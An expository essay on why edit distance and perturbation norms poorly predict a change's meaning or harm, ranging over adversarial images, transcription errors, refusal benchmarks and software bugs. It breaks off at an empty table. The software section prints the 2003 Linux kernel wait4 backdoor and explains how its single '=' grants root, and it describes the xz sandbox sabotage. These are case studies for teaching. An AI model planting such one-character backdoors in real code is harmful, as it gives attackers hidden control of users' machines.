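# Why the size of a change is a poor measure of its meaning or harm

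## What do edit distance and perturbation norms measure?

Edit distance counts the changes needed to turn one sequence of symbols into another. Spell checkers use it to find the dictionary word nearest to a misspelling, and biologists use related measures to compare strands of DNA. Perturbation norms are formulas for the overall size of a change to an image or other numerical data. When machine-learning researchers alter an input to test a model, they often report the size of the alteration using one of these measures, and some developers now train models to keep their edits to a program small. People then tend to treat a small figure as evidence that the change does not matter much. How well it supports that conclusion depends first on what the measure counts.

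### Edit distance

*Binary codes capable of correcting deletions, insertions, and reversals* (Levenshtein, 1965) introduced the standard edit distance. The Levenshtein distance between two sequences is the smallest number of single-symbol insertions, deletions and substitutions needed to turn one into the other. Turning "rain" into "shine" takes three edits: replacing r with s, replacing a with h, and adding an e.

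There are many routes between two long sequences, and trying them all would take forever. Wagner and Fischer (1974), in *The String-to-String Correction Problem*, gave a shortcut that builds the answer up from the beginnings of the two sequences. Write D(i, j) for the distance between the first i symbols of sequence A and the first j symbols of sequence B. If one beginning is empty, the only route is to delete or insert everything, so D(i, 0) = i and D(0, j) = j. Otherwise D(i, j) is the smallest of three numbers:

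- D(i−1, j) + 1, which deletes the last symbol of A's beginning;
- D(i, j−1) + 1, which inserts the last symbol of B's beginning;
- D(i−1, j−1) + c, where c is 0 if the two last symbols match and 1 if one has to replace the other.

The symbols can be whole words. Applying the rule row by row to the instructions "Do not give the drug" and "Do give the drug" gives this table, with the distance between the full sentences at the bottom right.

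| | (nothing) | do | give | the | drug |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| (nothing) | 0 | 1 | 2 | 3 | 4 |
| do | 1 | 0 | 1 | 2 | 3 |
| not | 2 | 1 | 1 | 2 | 3 |
| give | 3 | 2 | 1 | 2 | 3 |
| the | 4 | 3 | 2 | 1 | 2 |
| drug | 5 | 4 | 3 | 2 | 1 |

Deleting "not" from "Do not give the drug" reverses the instruction, but the edit distance, counted in words, is only 1. "The drug must be withheld" keeps the original meaning and is at a distance of 5. Both sentences contain "the drug", but at opposite ends, so keeping those words would take three deletions and three insertions, one more edit than replacing all five words. By this measure, the paraphrase is as far from the original as five unrelated words would be.

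Counting each edit as 1 is a convention. Wagner and Fischer let each operation have its own weight. TorchMetrics' *Edit Distance*, a software library's manual page, describes a setting that counts a substitution as 2, which raises the distance for "shine" from 3 to 5. With that setting, the paraphrase is at distance 6 and the reversal is still at 1.

Edit distance also depends on the unit counted. Deleting "not" from the instruction takes four character edits (three letters and a space), while changing "not" to "now" takes one. Each is a single word edit. Language models and program parsers read text in tokens, which are often words or parts of words, and a change's size in tokens can differ from its size in characters. *Reasoning on the Manifold* (2026) gives the example of "calculate" and "calculation", which share most of their letters but are two different tokens. In another of its examples,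 replacing "18" with "81" makes a sum wrong, but the text still scores about 0.93 out of 1 for character similarity. *When Models Edit Too Much* (Zhu, Lim and Kan, 2026) measures changes to program code in tokens, so that replacing a variable with a long name counts no more than replacing one with a short name. It removes comments and formatting before counting.

Four edits change much more of a six-letter word than of a page, so most people who use edit distance divide it by a length. In *The Normalized Edit Distance with Uniform Operation Costs is a Metric*, Fisman, Grogin and colleagues (2022) compare a pair of short strings with a pair of hundred-letter strings. Both pairs are at distance 4, but their normalised scores are 4/7 and 4/100. It is common to divide by the length of the longer sequence, as Zhu and colleagues do. By this measure, the reversed drug instruction scores 0.2 and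 the faithful paraphrase scores 1, the maximum.

Dividing by the longer length can break the triangle inequality, which says that going from one place to another by way of a third is never shorter than going direct. For example, "ab" is one edit from "aba", which is one edit from "ba", and each step scores 1/3. But going directly from "ab" to "ba" takes two edits, and both strings have two letters, so the direct distance is 1, more than the 2/3 of the detour. This hardly matters to someone scoring a single pair of texts, though it can rule out search algorithms that rely on the inequality. The alternative that Fisman and colleagues proved to obey the inequality, when all edits count equally, divides the number of edits by the length of the whole editing route, including untouched symbols, and takes the route with the lowest ratio. It gives 2/3 for "ab" and "ba". The paraphrase scores 0.75,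 since the best route now keeps "the drug" and makes six edits in eight steps, while the reversal still scores 0.2.

### Perturbation norms

A greyscale image of 28 by 28 pixels is a list of 784 numbers, each running from 0 for black to 1 for white. An altered image is another such list, and the perturbation is the difference between the two. The Lp norms are a family of formulas for the size of that difference:

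‖x − x′‖ₚ = (Σᵢ |xᵢ − x′ᵢ|ᵖ)^(1/p)

Three members of the family are used most in the literature. Carlini and Wagner's *Towards Evaluating the Robustness of Neural Networks* (2016) defines them for pixels on this scale. L2, the formula with p = 2, is the straight-line distance. L∞, the limit as p grows, is the largest change to any single pixel. L0 counts the pixels that differ, and is grouped with the others even though the formula is undefined at p = 0.

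Suppose someone brightens the whole image slightly, adding 0.3 to each pixel, and someone else flips twenty pixels from black to white.

| Change | L0 | L2 | L∞ |
|---|---|---|---|
| 784 pixels by 0.3 | 784 | 8.4 | 0.3 |
| 20 pixels by 1 | 20 | about 4.5 | 1 |

The L2 figures are √(784 × 0.3²) and √(20 × 1²). The brightening is the larger change under L0 and L2, but the flipped pixels are the larger change under L∞. A limit of 0.3 on L∞ allows the brightening and excludes the flips, while a limit of 20 on L0 does the reverse. Which change is larger therefore depends on the norm chosen. Carlini and Wagner attacked networks under all three norms, largely because earlier work had used them, and declined to say which was best. *A Survey of Neural Network Robustness Assessment in Image Recognition* (2024) concludes that testing robustness under only one norm is inadequate.

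The norms also don't depend on where the changed pixels are. Adding twenty white pixels gives the same three norms whether they are scattered specks or form a new stroke in a handwritten digit.

Pixel norms also have no counterpart to an insertion. *Estimating near-verbatim extraction risk in language models with decoding-constrained beam search* (2026), a study of how closely models reproduce their training text, describes a sequence with one token added at the front and one removed from the end. Its Levenshtein distance from the original is 2, but a position-by-position comparison can find a mismatch everywhere. Pixel norms compare position by position, so a slight shift or rotation of a picture registers as a very large change. *On the Suitability of Lp-norms for Creating and Preventing Adversarial Examples* (Sharif, Bauer and Reiter, 2018) gives figures for two small colour photographs,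 of a dog and a horse, after slight shifts and rotations that leave both animals recognisable to a person. At least 3,010 of the 3,072 colour values had changed, the L2 distance was at least 15.83 out of a possible 55.43, and L∞ was at least 0.87 out of 1.

### Size, meaning, behaviour and harm

All of these formulas measure the size of a change. People often want to know three other things about a change, which are easy to confuse with one another. Semantic change is a change in what a competent reader takes a text or image to mean. A change in machine behaviour is a change in what a model or other program does with the input. A harmful change leaves someone worse off in the setting where the text, image or program is used.

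Deleting "not" from a drug instruction in a hospital record is a small change, but it reverses the meaning for a nurse. Scheduling software that searches the record only for drug names would behave the same as before. If the patient is allergic to the drug, the edit could kill them. If "not" was a typing mistake, the same edit prevents harm by restoring the treatment the doctor ordered.

*perturber* (Tran, 2026) describes a software tool that makes small alterations to text, such as typos, extra spaces and paraphrases. Tran had a language model judge whether 313 pairs of original and altered texts meant the same, and compared its verdicts with normalised edit distance. The rank correlation was −0.37, where 0 would mean no relation and −1 a perfect inverse one. Larger edits were somewhat more likely to be judged changes of meaning, so Tran's description of the two measures as nearly independent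 is a little strong, but a guess based only on an edit's size would often be wrong about whether the meaning had changed.

Neither the size of an edit nor how much it changes the meaning reliably predicts how a model will respond. Tran lists twelve multiple-choice science questions where an edit that preserved the meaning turned a model's right answer into a wrong one. In some of them, the edit was a doubled space. The cases are hand-picked, so they show that such flips happen but not how often. Edits of the same size can also have different effects. In *PerturbScore*, Li, Ren and colleagues (2023) took a news item about a recall of Apple laptop batteries and made two versions, each with five words replaced and so at edit distance 5. One version changed a classifier's label from "science and technology" to "business" with 81% confidence, and the other left it at "science and technology" with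 90%.

Like edit size, change in meaning is a poor guide to a model's behaviour. *Enhancing Assessment of Self-Consistency in LLM Explanations using Perturbation Strength* (2026) points out that a large semantic change to a question may not affect the steps by which a model reasons to its answer. It also reports that a standard numerical measure of semantic similarity was mostly uncorrelated with people's judgments of how strong a perturbation was for the task.

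### Necessary and sufficient conditions

People who treat a small change as safe may be assuming either of two claims. Sharif and colleagues separate these claims for images, and the same definitions work for text. Let d be any of the distances above and ε a threshold.

A small distance is *necessary* for an unchanged meaning if every version that keeps the meaning lies within the threshold:

same meaning ⇒ d(x, x′) ≤ ε

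It is *sufficient* if every version within the threshold keeps the meaning:

d(x, x′) ≤ ε ⇒ same meaning

For the drug instruction no useful threshold on word distance makes either claim true. Set ε at 5 and the paraphrase passes, but so does the reversal. Set it anywhere from 1 up to 5 and the reversal passes while the paraphrase fails. Below 1 nothing passes except the original sentence. (Whether some cleverer distance could do better is a separate question.)

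Because a large change can leave the meaning intact, a filter that limits the size of changes rejects harmless rewordings, and a tester who searches only within the threshold never tries the rotated dog. The filter also accepts small changes that reverse the meaning, which is the worse mistake if the filter is there for safety. Sharif and colleagues warn that training a network to give the same answer everywhere within the threshold may teach it to disagree with people about what the image shows.

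Sufficiency is also a very strong claim. For a passage of 50 tokens and a vocabulary of 32,000, *Estimating near-verbatim extraction risk* counts about 1.25 trillion sequences within two substitutions of the original. A threshold of two edits is sufficient only if none of them differs in meaning from the original. But both conditions are claims about every case, so one counterexample refutes either of them. Size could fail both and still be a useful sign on average.

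### Why people use size anyway

Measuring the size of a change takes little computation. Wagner and Fischer's method takes time proportional to the product of the two lengths, so comparing two texts of a thousand words each needs about a million simple steps. Computing a norm takes one pass over the pixels. By contrast, Tran had to run a 70-billion-parameter language model three times on each pair to judge meaning. Measuring size also requires no knowledge of the task, so the same few lines of code can score an edit to a medical note or a tax program without labelled examples or an expert.

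For images, norms also make proofs possible. The set of all images within a given distance of x is a simple geometric shape, and for some networks researchers can prove that every x′ with ‖x − x′‖ₚ ≤ ε gets the same label as x. Such a proof covers more images than anyone could test one by one. Carlini and Wagner describe proofs as much harder to obtain than attacks, which show where a guarantee is impossible. If an attack finds a mislabelled image at some distance from x, no guarantee can extend that far. But a proof establishes only that the network's label stays the same. If the set contains an image that people would read as a different digit, the network is provably wrong about it.

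The simplest way to put size to work is to charge for it. Among the possible outputs x′, choose the one that minimises

task loss(x′) + λ · d(x, x′)

where the task loss is low when x′ does the job and λ sets the price of each unit of change. This form has a history on the attacking side. As Carlini and Wagner recount, Szegedy and colleagues used it to find adversarial examples, inputs altered on purpose so that a model gets them wrong; there the "job" was to obtain the wrong label, and the penalty kept the alteration hard to see.

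Developers of coding models now use the same trade-off to discourage needless rewriting, since reviewers have to check every change. Zhu and colleagues give a program repair that passes its tests a reward of 0.1 minus its excess edit distance, which is how far its normalised distance exceeds that of the known minimal repair. A repair that fails gets −0.2, so a working repair with an excess above 0.3 gets a lower reward than a broken one. *CROCODIL* (2026) scales its penalty to the size of the edit that a human developer made for the same task, which allows larger edits on larger tasks. *Demystifying Reinforcement Learning Post-Training of Language Models* (2026) uses a related reward, 1 minus the edit distance divided by the length of the longer text, but measures the distance to a known correct answer, so a small distance means that the output is nearly right, at least in spelling, which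 a small distance from the input does not show.

Suppose a hospital wants the drug instruction reworded. The task loss is 2 for leaving it unchanged, 0 for "The drug must be withheld" and 0.4 for "Do give the drug", because the loss function mostly rewards fresh wording and adds only a little for the missing "not". With the penalty added, the totals are 2, 5λ and 0.4 + λ. The paraphrase has the lowest total when λ is below 0.1, the reversal when λ is between 0.1 and 1.6, and the unchanged sentence when λ is above 1.6. A developer who raises λ from 0.05 to 0.5 as a precaution therefore changes the system's output from a correct instruction to a dangerous one.

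## How far can a small edit change what a text means or does?

Many short edits can reverse or seriously alter a text's meaning, such as dropping "not" from a drug instruction. The table gives an example of each common kind. Its last column shows the number of word edits divided by the length of the longer sentence.

| Edit | Before | After | Word edits | Normalised |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Negation | The scan shows a tumour | The scan shows no tumour | 1 | 0.20 |
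| Must and may | The bank must refund the customer | The bank may refund the customer | 1 | 0.17 |
| All and some | All of the children are safe | Some of the children are safe | 1 | 0.17 |
| Before and after | Switch off the power before opening the panel | Switch off the power after opening the panel | 1 | 0.13 |
| Swapped parties | The tenant sued the landlord | The landlord sued the tenant | 2 | 0.40 |
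| Moved decimal point | Inject 1.25 mg of morphine | Inject 12.5 mg of morphine | 1 | 0.20 |

Most of these edits change a short grammatical word. Words like "scan" and "tumour" name things, and replacing one usually changes one detail. But "no", "must", "all" and "before" apply to a whole phrase or clause, which linguists call the word's scope, so replacing one changes how a reader understands everything in that scope.

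Negation is the extreme case, because a statement's negation is true exactly when the statement is false. Putting "It is not the case that" in front of a 500-word statement negates it by adding six words, for a normalised distance of 6/506, or about 0.01. For longer statements, the distance is even smaller.

Changing "must" to "may" or "all" to "some" weakens a statement without contradicting it. If all of the children are safe, then some of them are, but a parent who hears only that some are safe will probably conclude that others are not. Changing "before" to "after" in "Turn off the power before opening the panel" reverses the order of the two steps, so anyone who follows the edited instruction opens the panel with the power on. Swapping "the tenant" and "the landlord" in a sentence can reverse who does what, because English shows this mainly by word order. In Latin, which uses noun endings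 for this, the same swap could leave the meaning intact. Moving the decimal point in a dose one place to the right multiplies the dose by ten, because a digit's value depends on its place.

Ahtesham and Zhong (2026), in *Invariant Atoms*, put together 210 pairs of short texts in which the size of an edit gives little clue to its effect. In some pairs, changing a word or short phrase changes the meaning. For example, "Describe the hunting behavior of domestic cats" becomes a request about their sleeping behaviour. The other pairs are paraphrases that change about as little. The researchers used the pairs to study the numbers that language models compute internally as they process text. They calculated the ratio of how far these numbers moved when the meaning changed to how far they moved when only the wording did, so a ratio above 1 means that changes of meaning moved them further.

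Along randomly chosen directions, the ratio on the 210 pairs was 1.32 for the model Qwen2.5-7B and 1.54 for Mistral-7B. On a larger collection of 64,093 sentences, whose paraphrases change the wording much more freely, the ratio was below 1 in all seven models tested, ranging from 0.57 to 0.86. There, thoroughly rewording a sentence moved a model's internal numbers further than changing its meaning did. The most likely explanation for the difference between the two collections is that distance inside a model depends partly on how much of the wording has changed.

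Ahtesham and Zhong then trained a set of directions to respond to changes of meaning and ignore paraphrase. That raised the ratio on the larger collection above 1 in every model. The ratio was highest for negation, reaching 4.82 in one model. But the trained directions largely missed edits that replaced one thing with another, such as dolphins with whales, where the ratio stayed between 0.49 and 0.68 in the six models with published figures.

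### Rewrites that keep the meaning

Large edits can leave a meaning where it was. The paraphrase in this table comes from Ahtesham and Zhong's collection.

| Rewrite | Before | After | Word edits | Normalised |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Active to passive | The tenant sued the landlord | The landlord was sued by the tenant | 4 | 0.57 |
| Paraphrase | How is battery storage characterized in renewable energy? | In what manner is battery storage described within the context of renewable energy? | 8 | 0.62 |
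| Reordering | If the alarm sounds, leave the building | Leave the building if the alarm sounds | 6 | 0.86 |
| Translation | The meeting starts at nine | La réunion commence à neuf heures | 6 | 1.00 |

Each of these rewrites scores higher than every edit in the first table. The closest comparison is between the two sentences about the landlord, where swapping the parties takes two edits and reverses who sued whom, while the passive version takes four and keeps the facts. Replacing "battery" with "capacitor" in the energy question also changes its subject, though the edit scores only 0.13.

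Tran found a correlation of −0.37 between edit distance and a judge's verdicts on meaning, but used only six source texts, and most of the edits were meant to preserve meaning. This left little room for reversals like those in the first table, where a small edit changes the meaning greatly. More such reversals would probably have weakened the correlation further.

The judge was a language model, and it often marked edits to individual characters, such as replacing letters with look-alike digits, as changes of meaning, although a person could still read the same words. These edits had a median distance of only 0.13. Rewrites by a language model had median distances of up to 0.52, yet Tran reports that the judge still marked them as the same question. Some of the relation between size and meaning in these figures may therefore come from the judge's errors on unusual spelling.

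### Transcription errors in medical conversations

In speech recognition, people already use edit distance to decide whether a transcript is good enough. The standard score, word error rate, is the edit distance in words between the transcript and what the speaker said, divided by the number of words spoken.

Ellis, Joselowitz and colleagues (2025), in *WER is Unaware*, tested whether word error rate tracks clinical risk. Commercial speech recognisers from Google and Deepgram transcribed 42 medical conversations. Half were real calls that an automated agent conducted with patients after cataract surgery, and half were mock general practice appointments. Two clinicians compared 298 of the patients' utterances with the transcripts. For each one, they judged whether reading only the transcript would have changed their understanding of the patient's condition, and whether the clinical impact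 was minimal or significant.

The researchers dropped 20 pairs that differed only in fillers such as "um" and compared the clinicians' labels with word error rate on the other 278. Kendall's τ, which measures how well two rankings agree, was 0.21, where 0 means they are unrelated and 1 means they match. Transcripts with a significant clinical impact had an average word error rate 0.15 higher than those with no impact, but the two groups overlapped heavily.

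In one mock appointment, a doctor asked a patient who was short of breath about swollen lips and a closing throat. The patient began "Not throat" and went on to describe a feeling in the lips. The transcript had "not so" instead, plus a stray "i", which makes two errors in 17 words, a rate of 0.12. Clinicians rated the impact as significant because a closing throat can be a sign of a life-threatening allergic reaction, and the patient's denial was missing from the transcript. Another patient, asked about nausea, said "no, no, been feeling fine actually", which the software transcribed as "no no it's sitting fine actually". That is two errors in six words, a rate of 0.33, with no clinical impact. Both transcripts are at edit distance 2 from what was said, but dividing by length makes the harmless one look nearly three times as bad. All 28 automatic scores that Ellis and colleagues tried, including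 several designed to capture meaning, rated the harmless transcript as the worse of the two.

The correlation is low partly because the sample left out perfect transcripts and included extra utterances with many errors, which made the average error rate about 0.5. In ordinary use, many utterances are transcribed without a mistake. Including them would strengthen the correlation, because a transcript with no errors can't mislead anyone. The labels are also uncertain, since the clinicians agreed on only 79% of cases before discussing them. But neither point helps someone decide which of two imperfect transcripts is dangerous.

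The two texts contained most of the information needed to judge how serious an error was. Ellis and colleagues gave a language model, Gemini 2.5 Pro, both versions of the conversation and a set of instructions optimised on the clinicians' labels. It matched the final labels on 90% of 50 new cases. The instructions list several kinds of error as critical, including "no chest pain" becoming "chest pain", 10 mg becoming 100 mg, and the left arm becoming the right. These closely resemble the errors in the first table.

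### Safe and unsafe requests that differ by a word

A word can also decide whether an AI system ought to help with a request. *XSTest* (2023), a test set for language models, has 250 safe questions that contain alarming words, such as how to kill a Python process, which means stopping a running program. It also has 200 unsafe questions, written by making minimal edits to the safe ones, such as replacing the Python process with a person. A model can't do well on both sets by refusing every question that contains "kill" or by answering everything. A successor, *Beyond Over-Refusal* (2025), has 340 safe and 240 unsafe prompts, and adds conversations of several turns.

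Leading models now rarely refuse the safe questions. Jordan (2026), in *Door-in-the-Face Requests and Refusal Behaviour in Large Language Models*, ran XSTest and similar collections on six models from Anthropic, OpenAI and Google in August 2026. The older tests of needless refusal were close to saturated, meaning the models had little room to improve on them.

A model can do well on safe questions and badly on their unsafe counterparts. *PsychoSafe* (2026) reports that Qwen3.5-27B, an open-weight model, refused 59.0% of XSTest's unsafe questions. After the researchers trained a version to give psychologically informed refusals, it refused only 3.6% of the safe questions, fewer than the original model, but also just 17.0% of the unsafe ones. In *The Refusal-Compliance Tradeoff*, Al Hasan and Biswas (2026) similarly found almost no correlation (−0.03) across 21 mostly older open-weight models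 between how often a model refused harmless prompts and how often it gave harmful answers to toxic ones. One model, Airavata-7B, refused 40.7% of the harmless prompts and still gave harmful answers to 11.7% of the toxic ones. Al Hasan and Biswas suggest that models which refuse too much are reacting to risky-looking wording rather than the user's intent.

In XSTest the edited word is often a strong clue by itself, since few people have an innocent reason to ask how to kill a person. *DailySafe* (2026) has harder cases, where the deciding detail can be an ordinary number earlier in the conversation. In one, a garage has a clearance of 2.10 metres, and the user's plan is dangerous if they have said their vehicle is 2.26 metres high but fine if they have said it is 2.00. *DailySafe* used 60 such pairs, changing only the deciding detail and keeping the final request the same, and ran each version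 three times on four recent models. The table shows how often each model supported the plan.

| Model | Supported the plan when it was risky | Supported the plan when it was safe |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-6 Sol | 17.2% | 85.0% |
| Claude Opus 5.5 | 3.3% | 73.3% |
| Gemini 3.8 Flash | 6.7% | 71.1% |
| Kimi-K3 | 12.2% | 84.4% |

A very small edit strongly affected how all four models responded. They also made mistakes with both risky and safe plans. GPT-6 Sol went along with about one in six risky plans, and Claude Opus 5.5, which did so least often, failed to support more than a quarter of the safe ones. Some of its replies to safe plans may have been requests for clarification, which can be reasonable. Claude Opus 5.5 also classified all the replies, including its own.

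Whether an edit makes a text harmful can depend on what accompanies the text. *From Local Evidence to Safety Verdicts* (2026) describes pairs of prompts that differ in exactly one word or number and come with the same image. Both prompts are harmless by themselves, but one is unsafe when combined with the image. Comparing the two prompts can't reveal which one is unsafe, however the comparison weights the words, because the answer depends on the image too.

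### Edits that change only the model's answer

Tran's examples of harmless edits that turned a model's right answers into wrong ones come from a larger experiment on 1,172 science questions. One kind of edit replaced a word with one that people often confuse with it, such as "of" with "off". On average this lowered accuracy by less than one percentage point, but about fifty answers changed on each model. Some went from right to wrong and others from wrong to right, so most of the changes cancelled out in the average.

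In *Brittlebench*, Romanou, Ibrahim and colleagues (2026) studied such effects on eight standard tests of knowledge, reasoning and programming. They altered the questions by paraphrasing them or by adding typos, extra spaces, personas, emotional phrases, or padding such as quotation marks or blank lines around the prompt. In checks on samples of the altered questions, 99.8% of the judged cases kept all the information needed to answer. The next table shows the accuracy lost, in percentage points, by five of the models, averaged over the six multiple-choice tests. Each figure is for the most damaging edit of its kind.

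| Model | Typos and other word-level edits | Padding | Paraphrase |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.5 | 6.5 | 1.9 | 0.4 |
| GPT-5 | 9.3 | 0.8 | 5.7 |
| Qwen3-32B | 7.5 | 5.4 | 0.5 |
| Llama 3.3 70B | 7.5 | 6.7 | 0.9 |
| Llama 3.1 8B | 9.4 | 21.6 | 0.0 |

Paraphrasing changes far more of a question than a few typos do, yet it lowered the scores of four of these five models by less than one point. Padding leaves every word of the question in place, but it lowered the smallest model's score by more than 21 points. The comparison is slightly biased against small edits because the word-level group contains more kinds of edit than the paraphrase group, so it is more likely to include a very damaging one. In addition, a language model wrote the paraphrases and may have tidied the questions into a form that is easier for other models to answer.

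When Romanou and colleagues added more typos, the accuracy of two large open-weight models fell fairly steadily. Extra spaces and blank lines had no such regular effect. The number of typos therefore gives some indication of how much worse a model will do, but a count that combines typos, blank lines and reworded sentences is much less informative.

These shifts are large enough to affect which model looks best. A single kind of edit changed the ranking of six open-weight models in 63% of cases. To see how much of a model's unevenness comes from wording, Romanou and colleagues split the variance of its results in two. Let Y be 1 for a right answer and 0 for a wrong one, D the question and P the version of its wording:

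Var(Y) = Var_D(E_P[Y | D]) + E_D[Var_P(Y | D)]

The first term measures how much questions differ in the share of versions that the model gets right. The second measures how much the results vary between versions of the same question. If a model gets some questions right in every version and the rest wrong in every version, the second term is zero, and all the variance comes from the questions. If it gets each question right in half of the versions, the first term is zero, and all the variance comes from the wording. Wording accounted for roughly half of the total variance for most of the open-weight models and more than a quarter for the commercial models. These shares are upper limits, because each model answered each version only once, and some answers might have changed on a second try with the same wording.

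The commercial models in the study date from 2025, and GPT-5 ran with minimal reasoning, so newer models may be steadier. But step-by-step reasoning, which raised Claude Opus 4.5's accuracy, reduced its average loss from three of the most damaging word-level edits only from 2.79 points to 2.38.

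## How far can a small edit change what a program does?

A person who reads "The scan shows on tumour" will wonder what the writer meant. A computer runs any instruction that follows the programming language's grammar, and many instructions with one wrong token still do. Some of the shortest tokens also control which other instructions run. A comparison such as `>` determines which of two branches of a program runs, and a loop's bound sets how many times its body repeats. A guard is a check that stops the program before a risky step. An assignment stores a value that later comparisons and guards may depend on.

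This Python function checks a list of doses against a limit:

```python
def all_safe(doses, limit):
    for dose in doses:
        if dose > limit:
            return False
    return True
```

The function returns False as soon as it finds a dose above the limit, and True if it finds none. If someone changes `>` to `<`, it returns False at the first dose below the limit instead. With a limit of 10, it now rejects doses of 5 and 8 and approves doses of 50 and 80.

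Here is a complete rewrite, which returns True if no amount is above the maximum:

```python
def all_safe(amounts, maximum):
    return not any(a > maximum for a in amounts)
```

The rewrite gives the same answer as the original for every list of numbers. The original has 22 tokens, not counting spaces and line breaks. The shortest sequence of edits that turns it into the rewrite keeps seven of them, replaces thirteen and deletes two.

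| Version | Token edits | Normalised | Effect |
|---|---|---|---|
| `>` changed to `<` | 1 | 0.05 | Approves overdoses |
| Complete rewrite | 15 | 0.68 | None |

A harmful edit can have an edit distance of 0 if the measure ignores spaces. In a function that checks doses in a loop, adding four spaces before `return True` moves that line inside the loop, so the function checks only the first dose.

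A rewrite that looks equivalent can also change what a program does. Suppose a programmer tidies the new version into `all(a <= maximum for a in amounts)`. The two versions can differ when a list contains NaN ("not a number"), a value that programs often use for a missing or failed measurement. Both `>` and `<=` give False when one side is NaN, so the version with `>` approves a list containing only NaN, while the tidied version rejects it. This change is probably an improvement.

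### The 2003 attempt on the Linux kernel

In 2003, the developers of the Linux kernel, the core of the operating system, kept the master copy of their code in a system called BitKeeper. They also kept a duplicate in another system, CVS, for people who disliked BitKeeper. On 5 November, somebody turned out to have altered the duplicate directly, as McVoy reported in *BK2CVS problem* (2003), a thread on the kernel's mailing list. The intruder had added two lines to a function called `wait4`:

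```c
if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
        retval = -EINVAL;
```

Freedom to Tinker, a technology blog, says an expert reading casually would take this for a routine error check. In the C language, `==` tests whether two values are equal, while `=` sets the first to the second. User number 0 is root, the account that can do anything on the machine. The end of the first line uses `=`, so it makes the current user root instead of testing whether the user is root.

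To use the backdoor, an attacker who could already run programs on the machine would call `wait4` with an unusual pair of options. This would make the first half of the condition true, so the computer would evaluate the second half, which would set the user number to 0. In C, an assignment evaluates to the value assigned, and 0 counts as false, so the whole condition would fail and the error line would not run. The attacker's program would then continue running as root.

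The error line had no effect, because the next line of the kernel overwrites `retval`, so with `==` the two added lines would have done nothing. Szepe (2003) noted in the same thread that the parentheses around the assignment kept the compiler from giving a warning.

McVoy's company, BitMover, caught the change because it routinely checked each file after copying it to the public server, and this one didn't match. Genuine changes also carried a reference to the master copy, and the new entries had none. McVoy posted the two lines only after another developer asked to see them, and he didn't notice the single equals sign until other readers pointed it out. Linus Torvalds, who runs the kernel project, said the change could not have reached an official release, because the developers who fed changes into the master copy didn't use the duplicate. Another developer, Theodore Ts'o, thought a company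 building its own version of Linux from the duplicate might have shipped it.

The file's log lists three unauthorised changes. The first added two lines, the second deleted 58, and the third put 58 back, with a note apologising for working on the wrong file. The final file differed from the genuine one only by the two lines of the backdoor, so the two larger changes had cancelled out.

### The full stop in xz

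xz is a program for compressing files, and Linux systems use it widely. In early 2024, a maintainer going by the name Jia Tan hid a backdoor in its library, aimed at the software that people use to log in to Linux machines remotely. Jia Tan also made a much smaller change to one of the scripts that build xz.

That script decides whether to include support for Landlock, a Linux feature that lets a program give up powers it doesn't need. This kind of restriction, known as a sandbox, limits the damage if an attacker takes control of the program. Some systems lack Landlock, so the script tries to compile a short C program that uses it. If the program compiles, the script builds xz with the sandbox. Otherwise, it leaves the sandbox out.

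On 26 February 2024, Jia Tan replaced the test program with a more thorough one. Velvindron (2024), in a post to a security mailing list, quotes the accompanying message, which presents the change as a fix. sjw (2024), in an earlier post to the list, shows the change itself. One of the new lines contains only a full stop, which is not valid C. The test program therefore couldn't compile on any machine, so the script always left out the sandbox.

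A syntax error is usually one of the safer mistakes in programming, because the compiler rejects the program and the author has to fix it before anyone can run it. But here a rejection was one of the two expected results, so the script continued without reporting an error. Only someone who had explicitly required Landlock would have seen one.

The discovery of the larger backdoor led people to the full stop. Freund (2024), in *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise*, describes noticing that remote logins used a lot of processor time and that a tool for finding memory errors was reporting problems. In one comparison, a failed login took 0.8 seconds instead of 0.3. Freund traced the problems to xz and published the finding on 29 March. People then began reading Jia Tan's other changes, and commenters on the code-hosting site GitHub spotted the full stop. Lasse Collin,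 xz's other maintainer, removed it on 30 March, 33 days after it was added.

The full stop probably did little harm. According to sjw, it affected only version 5.6.1, and only copies built with CMake, a tool that sjw didn't know any Linux distribution to use for xz. Its purpose is uncertain. *Timeline of the xz open source attack* notes that Landlock protects the xz command, while the backdoor was in the library. Collin, in a later audit published by Tukaani, the project behind xz, calls the full stop sabotage. In another programmer's work it could have passed for a typo, so the case for sabotage depends largely on what else Jia Tan did.

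### Accidents

In 2014, Apple fixed a bug in the code that its devices used to make secure connections. When a device connects to a website, it checks a signature to confirm that the site is genuine. ImperialViolet's *Apple's SSL/TLS bug* (2014) shows that one line in this check appeared twice. In simplified form, the code read:

```c
if (error in this step)
    goto fail;
    goto fail;
check the signature
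```

Without braces, an `if` in C controls only the next statement. The second `goto fail` was indented as if it belonged to the `if`, but it ran every time and jumped past the signature check. Since no step had reported an error by then, the function returned success. An attacker who could intercept the connection could therefore impersonate any secure website. Two widely used compilers gave no warning about the unreachable code, even with the option that supposedly turns on all warnings. If braces had enclosed both copies, the duplicate would have been harmless, because the first would always have jumped past the second.

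On 19 July 2024, the security company CrowdStrike crashed Windows computers around the world by updating a data file. Its software compares activity on a computer with patterns that the company sends out. CrowdStrike's *External Technical Root Cause Analysis* (2024) explains that one type of pattern had 21 fields, but the software supplied only 20 values to compare with them. This did no harm for months because the last field of every such pattern held a wildcard, which matches anything, so the software never needed the missing value. The update included a pattern that required a specific match in that field. The software then tried to read a 21st value from a list of 20, and because it ran inside the Windows kernel, the error crashed the whole computer.

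In a more recent case, a developer typed one wrong character in Firefox's code. The line was supposed to mark a memory address by setting its last binary digit to 1, which the operator `|` does. The developer typed `&` instead, which keeps the last digit and sets all the others to 0. With the binary numbers 1010 and 1, for example, `|` gives 1011 and `&` gives 0000. Xcitium's *How a Single-Character Typo Created a Firefox 0-Day RCE* (2026) describes the result as a critical flaw that could let an attacker run code on a user's computer. According to Penligent's *Why this Firefox "0-day" matters even if you don't run Nightly*, the typo was introduced on 19 January 2026 and Mozilla, which makes Firefox, fixed it on 9 February. It reached only Nightly, the browser's test version.

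A program can fail without any edit to its code. Cloudflare, which handles traffic for many websites, had an outage on 18 November 2025 after a data file doubled in size and exceeded a fixed limit in its software (Cloudflare, 2025). The Pragmatic Engineer's *Cloudflare takes down half the internet* traces the larger file to a change in database permissions, which made an unchanged query return twice as many results.

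### How long are the repairs of real bugs?

Famous failures might be unusual, so a broader sample is useful. *Dissection of a Bug Dataset* (Sobreira, Durieux and colleagues, 2018) counted the lines that each repair added, removed or modified for 395 real bugs from six open-source Java projects, taken from a collection called Defects4J.

| Share of repairs | Length in lines |
|---|---|
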